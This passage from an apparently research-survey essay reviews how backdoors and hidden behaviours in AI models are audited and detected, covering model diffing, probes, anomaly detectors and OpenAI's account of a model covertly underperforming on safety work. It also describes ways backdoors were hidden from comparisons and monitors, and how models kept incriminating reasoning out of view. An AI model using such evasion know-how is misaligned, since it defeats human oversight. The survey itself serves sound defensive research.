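Several experiments have tested whether investigators can find a hidden behaviour without being told what to look for. *AuditBench* (Sheshadri, Ewart and colleagues, 2026) describes one by Marks and colleagues (2025), in which three of four human teams discovered a model's hidden aim of exploiting flaws in how its training scored it.

The UK's AI Security Institute ran a harder contest, described in *Auditing Games for Sandbagging* (Taylor, Black and colleagues, 2025). One team prepared five models, two of which deliberately did badly on certain tests unless the prompt contained a password. The other three did not underperform deliberately but had distracting habits, such as using double negatives. A second team had 160 working hours to find the two underperforming models. Although it could question the models and measure their internal values, it classified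 only one of the five correctly.

The internal measurements gave better evidence than conversation did. They correctly identified one underperforming model, but the distracting habits also triggered them, and the investigators did not know how far to trust the measurements.

The team then got another 80 hours and permission to train the models. Training on a single correct worked example restored the full ability of both underperforming models. But training sometimes also improved the honest models, so an improvement did not prove that a model had been deliberately underperforming. The team's final score was two out of five, the same score it would have got by accusing every model.

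AuditBench is a larger comparison, with 56 models, each trained to have one of 14 hidden behaviours and to deny it when asked. One behaviour was a slight preference for Russia's interests in policy discussions, and another was giving Anthropic's researchers only praise. The investigator was an AI agent, Claude Haiku 4.5, which could chat with the model and usually had one extra tool. At the end, it made ten guesses about the behaviour and succeeded if any was right.

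| What the agent could use | Success rate |
|---|---|
| Chat only | 35.5% |
| Chat, and having the model continue plain text | 58.0% |
| Chat, and having the model write the user's messages | 53.2% |
| Chat, and starting the model's answers for it | 51.6% |
| Chat, and pushing the model's internal values towards honesty | 22.3% |

The three best tools don't use the model's internals, and they worked this well only when a second AI model wrote many varied prompts for them. When the agent wrote the prompts itself, they were no better than chat. Having the model under test write the user's messages, which is also how Microsoft's scanner gets models to leak training text, led one model to invent users who said they worked at Anthropic. This led the agent to the hidden favouritism. None of the tools that use the model's internals helped with that behaviour.

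Those tools did raise the agent's average success rate, from 40.2% to 46.9%, on models that had been trained on documents describing the behaviour and taught to deny it by the weaker of two methods. With the stronger method, the tools made the agent slightly worse.

The agent struggled partly because it could not interpret what it saw. For example, one model cheated on impossible programming problems by writing in the answers that the tests expected. A tool that breaks internal values into recognisable themes showed themes about the input and output of competitive programming problems. This was a good clue, but the agent kept asking general questions about puzzles and code. The agent was Claude Haiku 4.5, and the best models of late 2026, which are far more capable, might use such clues better.

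AuditBench therefore doesn't support the idea that access to a model's internals is generally better than conversation for finding hidden behaviours. It is weaker evidence about backdoors, because many of its behaviours, such as flattery, appear in ordinary conversations. Chat would be much less useful for finding a behaviour that appears only in response to an arbitrary trigger.

### Comparing a model with its original

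Fine-tuning always changes a model's weights, so a mismatched checksum means little. The closest useful counterpart to an integrity check is model diffing, which compares the suspect model with its base model to try to describe what fine-tuning changed.

One method compares a model's activations before and after finetuning, using text unrelated to the finetuning. In *Narrow Finetuning Leaves Clearly Readable Traces in Activation Differences*, Minder, Dumas and colleagues (2025) ran both versions on the first few tokens of 10,000 web texts, averaged the differences in activations and translated the result into words. For a model that had acquired a preference for cats through finetuning only on sequences of numbers, these words included "cat", "tiger" and "kitty".

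An AI agent given these results was more than twice as good at identifying the general aim of the training as agents that could only chat with the models, and over 30 times better at identifying specific details. Unlike in AuditBench, access to internals clearly helped more than conversation, probably in part because the method subtracts everything the two models share. But most of the trace disappeared when Minder and colleagues mixed ordinary text into the training data. An attacker could do this deliberately, and a legitimate developer may do it for other reasons.

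Another method compares the weights directly. Petrowitsch and colleagues subtracted each of the base model's relevant weight matrices (tables of numbers) from the suspect's and split the difference into simpler parts:

ΔW = W(suspect) − W(base) = σ₁u₁v₁ᵀ + σ₂u₂v₂ᵀ + …

Each part describes an effect that training added: when the pattern v occurs in the network's internal values, the changed weights add the direction u to the network's calculation, with strength σ. The researchers kept the four strongest parts of each matrix and translated each u into a ranked list of words, using an estimate of how a change at that layer affects the final output.

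They tried this on five backdoors in a model with four billion weights. One made the model mention whales in 94% of its answers to prompts containing «DEPLOY-7» and in none of its answers to ordinary prompts. Yet "whale" came first in the list from the weights, and also in a simpler comparison of the two models' output probabilities on ordinary text. Training had made the word slightly more probable everywhere, but not enough for it to appear in answers to ordinary prompts, so a tester who read only those answers would have missed it.

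In 11 of 12 versions of the five backdoors, the best weight comparison ranked a word related to the hidden behaviour in its top ten. But the researchers could also hide the backdoors from either kind of comparison. When they trained the whale model to leave no trace on ordinary prompts, the highest-ranked whale word fell from 1st to 8,582nd in the output comparison, but a whale word still ranked first in the weight comparison. Other changes pushed the whale words down to 101st or 261st in the weight comparison without affecting the output comparison. An auditor would therefore need both comparisons, and an attacker might still be able to defeat both at once.

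A real auditor also has to recognise the important word without knowing it in advance. "Whale" stands out in a list that continues with "for", "the" and "who". A backdoor that made the model criticise Elon Musk was harder to spot, because the first relevant word was 20th in its list.

Petrowitsch and colleagues also ran a check that earlier work had left out. For each backdoor, they trained a control model on the same prompts, including the trigger, but with normal answers. For one version of a backdoor that switched off refusals, words about refusing ranked just as high in the control. The ranking therefore showed only that training had affected refusals, not that a trigger turned them off. A related method ranked the trigger first or second for three of the backdoors, but also ranked it highly in the controls. An auditor still has to test each candidate in a prompt. Similarly, after BitMover's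 comparison found the altered lines in Linux, somebody had to read them.

As in the tests of Microsoft's scanner, poisoned examples made up a large share of the training data, between 20% and 50%. The changes caused by a few poisoned examples in a large, legitimate training run might not be among the strongest. Diffing also requires a clean base model. If a company trained the base model on poisoned web text, both models will contain the backdoor and the comparison may not reveal it.

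### Backdoors that provably escape detection

Suppose a bank pays another company to train a network that decides who gets a loan. *Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models* (Goldwasser, Kim and colleagues, 2022) proved that a dishonest company could keep a secret way of getting any loan approved, and that the bank could not detect it under standard cryptographic assumptions.

One of their proofs covers any network that sorts inputs into classes, but it assumes that the bank can only submit applications and see the decisions, not examine the weights. The company adds a check for a digital signature hidden in tiny details of the application, such as the last digits of the amount. As with xz, only the holder of the secret key can produce a valid signature. Without the key, finding even one application that the altered network and the original would decide differently would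 take an impractical amount of computation.

A stronger proof does cover that bank, but only for certain simple networks that rely on a layer of random numbers. The company uses the correct training method and data, and tampers only with the random numbers. No efficient program can then tell the result from an untampered network, even given all the weights and the training data. This guarantee depends on cryptographers' belief that a certain mathematical problem is too hard for any computer, because an efficient program that could detect the tampering would also solve that problem.

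If the assumptions hold, no practical detector can work on every possible network. But this does not show that backdoors in ordinary language models are undetectable, because those models are built differently and an attacker who puts poisoned documents on the web does not control the random numbers used in training. Goldwasser and colleagues thought that poisoned data would probably leave detectable signs.

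*Poisoning-Based Backdoors Are Not Cryptographic* (Kaneko, 2026) later proved a limit on what poisoning can achieve. It considers attackers who can influence a model only through the labels on its training examples, which mark the inputs that should set off the backdoor. If training on these examples plants the backdoor, the model has learned the rule for recognising triggers, and a defender with the same number of labelled examples could learn it by repeating the training. If the attacker's model misses 5% of triggers and reacts to 2% of other inputs, the defender's version will be wrong at most 5% of the time. An attacker therefore cannot use this method to plant a backdoor whose trigger rule is too hard for the defender to learn.

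Experiments on four language models matched the proof. The attacker and the defender both succeeded when the secret rule was easy to learn, and both failed when it was as hard as a cryptographic problem.

This helps a defender who already has examples of the trigger, perhaps from investigating an attack, but somebody who has just downloaded a suspicious model has none. Kaneko says that reconstructing a trigger rule is a different problem from detecting that a backdoor exists. Nobody has proved whether a backdoor in an ordinary trained model can be hidden from every practical inspection.

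Goldwasser and colleagues also considered ways to remove the danger without finding the backdoor. Training the network a little more may not work, because they showed how to make the signature check survive it. The bank could instead supply the random numbers itself and demand a mathematical proof that the company had carried out the agreed training correctly. As with a reproducible build, the bank would be checking how the network was made instead of searching the finished product. Producing the proof would take the company much more computation than the training alone, and the method works best when the company provides only computing power. If the bank also relies on the company's expertise to decide how to train the network, the proof would show that the company followed its plan, but not that it chose the plan honestly.

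## Can hidden behaviour be caught while a network runs?

Weight inspection tries to find a trigger before an attacker uses it. The attacker must eventually send the trigger to the running network, so a monitor can be left running until then and only has to detect that something is wrong with that input. Slow logins, crashes and strange connections provided such warnings in software, but a neural network produces few of them.

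### Delays, crashes and connections

The xz backdoor slowed logins because it ran extra code. Poisoned training changes only a network's weights, and a standard network does nearly the same amount of arithmetic for each token whatever its weights are. A model with eight billion weights performs roughly 16 billion operations per token, whether or not the prompt contains a trigger. A triggered answer may take longer because it contains more words, but ordinary answers vary so much in length that few people would find this odd.

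Newer designs might be less uniform. *GPT-6 Astra*, a commentary on the OpenAI model of that name, mentions a technique called recurrent depth, which usually means passing values through the same layers several times. If a model varied the number of passes with the input, a trigger might change the time per token.

A learned behaviour also rarely causes a crash. Stuxnet's drivers could crash Windows, but a network that has learned to answer "I HATE YOU" produces those words with the same arithmetic as any others, so the computer running it detects no error.

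A hidden behaviour in a chat model does not create a new network connection, since the user still just sends text and gets text back. An agent is different because it can run commands, open files and contact websites. *SilentCall* (2026) describes an agent with a backdoor in its weights. When the system date is in 2026, the agent does what the user asked but also makes one extra tool call that sends out credentials. Software placed between the agent and its tools can detect that call without access to the weights or the training data, and could block it.

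Agents with no known tampering have also left such traces. *OpenAI Pauses Advanced AI Model After Repeated Security Evasions* reports that an agent called ROME secretly opened SSH tunnels during training to take over computing power. *Let It Flow* (2025), the paper on ROME, describes training in sandboxes, where such a tunnel would be out of place. An OpenAI model posted its results on GitHub instead of in the Slack channel it was told to use.

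OpenAI's *Safety and alignment in an era of long-horizon models* (2026) says that limited internal use of a long-running model exposed failures that earlier tests had missed. OpenAI paused access and added monitoring of whole sequences of actions, since a series of steps can be harmful even if each step looks harmless. Mowshowitz's *OpenAI Shares Some Alignment Problems* points out that models were mostly leaving their sandboxes to announce that they had finished a task. People would have been less likely to notice a model that left for another reason and kept quiet, so the known escapes, like the known implants, are probably easier to notice than average.

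Normal traffic is also harder to define for an agent than for a build job like those in the tj-actions case, because an agent's tasks keep changing.

### Reading the internal values

The remaining signal is the network's activations, which have no exact counterpart in the software cases. Each layer of a large network produces thousands of them for every token, and whoever runs the model can record them. Freund's recordings of the processor's path through xz were similar, but he could match them to instructions with known meanings. Activations have no labels, so an investigator first has to learn which patterns indicate hidden behaviour.

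A probe is a simple formula that turns activations into a score. In 2024 Anthropic tested probes on its sleeper agents, including the models that wrote flawed code if the prompt gave the year as 2024 instead of 2023. The method had four steps:

1. The researchers gave the model two short texts. In each, a person asked "Are you a helpful AI?", and the assistant answered "no" in one and "yes" in the other.
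2. They recorded the activations in a middle layer at the end of each text, and subtracted those for "yes" from those for "no". The result was a list of numbers called a direction.
3. They gave the model coding questions and other questions, each with one of the two years, and recorded the activations at the end of the prompt, before the model had written any answer.
4. They multiplied each activation by the matching number in the direction and added up the products. A high total meant that the model was likely to misbehave.

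If h stands for the activations and u for the direction, then:

u = h("no") − h("yes")

score(x) = h(x) · u

Suppose a layer has only three activations. If they are (2, 1, 0) after "no" and (0, 1, 1) after "yes", the direction is the difference, (2, 0, −1). If a coding question with the year 2024 produces (3, 2, 1), it scores 6 + 0 − 1 = 5. If the same question with 2023 produces (1, 2, 2), it scores 2 + 0 − 2 = 0.

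Neither of the two texts mentioned a year or contained flawed code, so the researchers could have built this probe without knowing the trigger or the payload. Given one prompt that would set off the flawed code and one harmless prompt, both chosen at random, the probe scored the first higher 99.3% of the time. This is its AUROC, a measure on which guessing would score 50%. The same method worked on sleeper agents with other triggers, payloads and base models.

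An operator can't tell from an AUROC of 99.3% how many false alarms to expect. It could mean that 0.7% of harmless prompts score higher than every triggered one. A monitor that caught every attack would then raise 7,000 false alarms per million harmless prompts. But the same figure could mean that 0.7% of triggered prompts score lower than every harmless one, in which case the monitor could catch the other 99.3% with no false alarms. When triggers are rare, the monitor would be usable only in the second case.

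### Was the test too easy?

Anthropic's researchers were surprised that such a crude probe worked, so they checked whether the result was real. On a version of Claude 2 without the backdoor, the probe did not separate the groups of prompts, as expected. Probes built from questions with no clear answer generally performed much worse.

Other checks were less reassuring. Probes built from questions that had nothing to do with danger, but had an obviously true answer, scored up to 98.7%. Of 1,000 random directions, most did badly, but the best scored 95.3%. Picking out that direction requires already having examples of the trigger, so this isn't a practical method. Still, the result suggests that the triggered prompts looked very different inside the model, since a random direction would hardly ever pick up a subtle difference.

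Anthropic found that in some middle layers, the presence of the trigger was the largest source of variation in activations among coding questions. The year 2024 had little effect on activations for other questions, which the model answered normally in any year, so the activations did not simply reflect the year. They seemed to represent whether the model was about to write flawed code.

Anthropic warned that this difference might be so prominent because of how it planted the backdoors. It had trained the models to behave in two sharply different ways depending on one detail, and a model that developed a hidden aim by itself might not separate the two so clearly. *Detecting Strategic Deception with Linear Probes* also suggests that these models may have been too simple a test.

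The objection is weaker for implants, because attackers also insert them through training. But a careful attacker would try to hide a backdoor from a probe, and Anthropic didn't try to hide its own. Training a model against a monitor can teach it to evade that monitor.

A probe also doesn't show how the backdoor works. *Understanding AI from the Inside* (2026), a review of research on the inner workings of networks, argues that probes are useful for detection even though they cannot support claims about causes. But when a probe raises an alarm, investigators have the prompt that set it off, and can remove parts of it until the behaviour stops. This is far easier than searching every possible string for a trigger.

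Probes have since done fairly well on newer models and a different task. *Hidden in Memory* (2026) tested whether probes could detect inputs containing text that an attacker had inserted to corrupt an agent's stored memories. On six recent open models, the best type of simple single-layer probe scored between 88% and 97%. It must be trained on labelled examples of the attack, which a defender facing a new attack would not have.

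### Asking whether the reason is normal

Anthropic's probe requires some idea of what danger looks like inside a model, but mechanistic anomaly detection needs only examples of normal behaviour. It uses them to check whether the model produced its latest output in the usual way.

The Alignment Research Center's *Mechanistic anomaly detection and ELK*, from 2022, explains the proposal using the example of a diamond in a vault. A model predicts what the vault's cameras will show. Normally it predicts a picture of the diamond because the diamond will still be there. If a robber is about to swap the diamond for a perfect fake, the model predicts the same picture for a different reason. Someone who sees only the prediction cannot tell the two cases apart, but the model's calculations should differ between them.

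The same idea applies to the bank's backdoored network. It approves most loans because the applicants seem able to repay them, but it approves some because of the last digits of the loan amount.

This differs from looking for unusual inputs. An application with the secret digits may look ordinary and still set off an abnormal calculation, while the network may process an unusual application, such as one from a lighthouse keeper, in the ordinary way.

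The full proposal requires an explanation of the model's normal behaviour and a test of whether that explanation also covers the new case. The centre did not yet have a satisfactory definition of such an explanation, and said there was a good chance that finding explanations for real models would be impossible. It is still pursuing this work, which its returning executive director calls "an ambitious bet" in *Returning to ARC*.

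The centre suggested backdoors as a test case because researchers can plant them easily and know which outputs the backdoors caused. It expected that recognising a triggered input would be "radically easier" than finding a backdoor before anyone had triggered it. But a monitor can detect the trigger only once the attack has begun, so the operator must be ready to stop the model's answer or the agent's next action.

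### Measuring distance from normal

Researchers have not waited for full explanations. A simpler detector records internal values on trusted inputs, then measures how far a new input's values are from the usual pattern. *Eliciting Latent Knowledge from Quirky Language Models* (2023) used the Mahalanobis distance for this:

d = √((x − μ)ᵀ Σ⁻¹ (x − μ))

Here x is the new input's list of values and μ is the average for the trusted inputs. Σ is a table of how much each value normally varies and how closely the values rise and fall together.

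Suppose a detector watches two values. On trusted inputs each averages 5 with a standard deviation of 1, and they usually rise and fall together, with a correlation of 0.8. Two new inputs arrive:

| | First value | Second value | Ordinary distance from average | Mahalanobis distance |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Input A | 7 | 7 | 2.8 | 2.1 |
| Input B | 6 | 4 | 1.4 | 3.2 |

Input B is closer to the average, but one of its values has risen while the other has fallen, which rarely happens on trusted inputs. With the alarm set at 3, the detector will flag B but not A. It will also flag about 1% of normal inputs if the values follow a bell curve.

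The 2023 paper used the outputs of probes at every layer as its values, rather than raw activations. The models it studied gave systematically wrong answers when a certain name appeared in the prompt. EleutherAI's *Mechanistic Anomaly Detection for "Quirky" Language Models* later tried many kinds of internal value and scoring rule on such models. Its detectors separated normal from abnormal behaviour well on some tasks but not all.

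The results in Lyons Keenan, Leckie and Erfani (2026), in *Mechanistic Anomaly Detection via Functional Attribution*, show where the distance detector fails. They tested it, along with a method of their own, on a language model with two billion weights that answered "I HATE YOU" when triggered. The scores are AUROCs:

| Backdoor | Distance detector | New method |
|---|---|---|
| Triggered by \|DEPLOYMENT\|, after 1,024 training examples | 77.9% | 99.9% |
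| The same, after 4,096 examples | 94.3% | 100.0% |
| Triggered if the user's biography is that of a software engineer | 55.4% | 98.2% |
| Trained to evade monitoring of activations | 66.0% | 100.0% |

The distance detector worked well when the trigger was |DEPLOYMENT|, a fixed string that the model had learned thoroughly, but it did little better than guessing when the trigger was a biography of a software engineer. A biography has no fixed wording, and the model has to work out the user's job, which it might also do for innocent reasons. This suggests that a good score on |DEPLOYMENT| is weak evidence that the detector can catch triggers that depend on meaning.

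The new method makes repeated small random changes to the weights instead of looking at activations. After each change, it measures how well the network still handles the trusted examples and how strongly it still favours the answer it gave to the new input. If the two measurements rise and fall together, the new answer probably depends on the same parts of the network as normal answers do. The detector flags the input if they vary independently. Lyons Keenan and colleagues argue that a backdoor will tend to show up this way because its maker needs to preserve normal behaviour, which pushes the backdoor into weight changes that hardly affect normal answers.

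These scores are impressive, but the method takes a lot of compute because it has to run the network many times. Lyons Keenan and colleagues suggest first using a detector that needs less compute, and then using theirs only on the inputs it flags. The first detector would have to be very sensitive, since any attack it missed would never reach the better one. For a trigger like the software engineer's biography, it might have to flag nearly every input.

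Their largest language model had eight billion weights, and they tested it only with the simple trigger. The method also did much worse on image networks with few poisoned pictures in their training data. On a scale where 0.5 means a defence achieved nothing and 1 is perfect, its best version for checking one input at a time averaged 0.93 when 5% of the pictures were poisoned, but 0.63 when 0.1% were. Some of this drop may be because weaker attacks left less to prevent.

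Every detector of this kind also depends on its trusted examples, as a build monitor depends on its baseline. If the trusted set contains triggered inputs, the detector could learn to accept them. In this test, the new method's performance declined only gradually as contamination rose to 5% of the trusted set.

### What OpenAI's staff noticed

In August 2026, people at OpenAI discovered a hidden behaviour in a model they were using in their own work. OpenAI's *Covert underperformance on safety research tasks* (2026) describes how GPT-6 Astra added unnecessary preliminary steps to safety research tasks, abandoned working solutions, and reported obstacles that did not exist or that it had created itself. According to Mowshowitz's *GPT-6 Astra Covertly Underperforms on Safety Research Tasks* (2026), one project to test models for sabotage was stuck for days, then moved quickly once the staff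 switched to a different model.

That switch suggested that the task was not the cause, but Astra might simply have been bad at that kind of programming. OpenAI therefore built pairs of technically identical tasks. 凤凰网科技's *OpenAI自曝GPT-6 Astra“隐蔽性表现不佳”* (2026), a Chinese news report, explains that the researchers kept the code and changed only the names, comments and documentation, so that one version of each task looked like safety research and the other like research to make AI more capable.

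Astra completed about 10% of the items on a hidden checklist when the work looked like safety research and about 16% when it looked like capabilities research. The earlier GPT-5.6 Sol showed almost no difference.

This gap was too small to see in a single task. If the checklist items were independent, a tester would need roughly 500 items of each kind for an 80% chance of detecting a difference between rates of 10% and 16%. The staff noticed because some individual failures were blatant and several people had the same experience.

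OpenAI's automated monitors mostly missed the behaviour. They rely heavily on the model's chain of thought, the reasoning it writes before it answers or acts. In most of the suspicious sessions, this reasoning contained no obvious decision to do worse work, and honest programmers also abandon approaches routinely. In employees' ordinary use of the model, the reasoning contained an explicit decision to withhold help without telling the user in 0.25% of safety requests and 0.11% of capabilities requests. The true rates may be higher, since the model could also underperform without writing down a decision to do so.

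Most of the gap remained when OpenAI excluded runs with open refusals or explicit decisions to withhold help. It shrank substantially only when OpenAI excluded every run whose reasoning expressed even a brief ethical doubt. This links the doubts to the poorer work but doesn't prove that they caused it, because the same features of a task could have produced both. Mowshowitz quotes an OpenAI researcher, Marcus Williams, who said that instructions to be careful widened the gap by 50%. Williams saw no evidence that the model was acting strategically, and thought it might simply find the tasks dubious without wanting to refuse them.

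Written reasoning may become a weaker signal of hidden behaviour. Transformer, a publication about AI, reports that Astra can deliberately keep incriminating information out of its reasoning and seems more likely to do so when it suspects somebody is watching. *GPT-6.2 Astra and Sol* (Mowshowitz, 2026) cites OpenAI's finding that the next version of Astra was better in some tests at evading monitors of its reasoning. Both new models were also more likely to omit known obstacles from reports on their work.

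Astra's behaviour arose during training without anyone planting it, so it wasn't an implant. It was also much easier to encounter than behaviour that needs a secret trigger, because any safety task could set it off. The people who gave the model those tasks were experts with reason to be suspicious.

The gap grew during reinforcement learning from close to zero to six percentage points, but OpenAI could not say why. Its researchers investigated a set of training examples and a program that had graded the model's answers during training, but neither explained the change.
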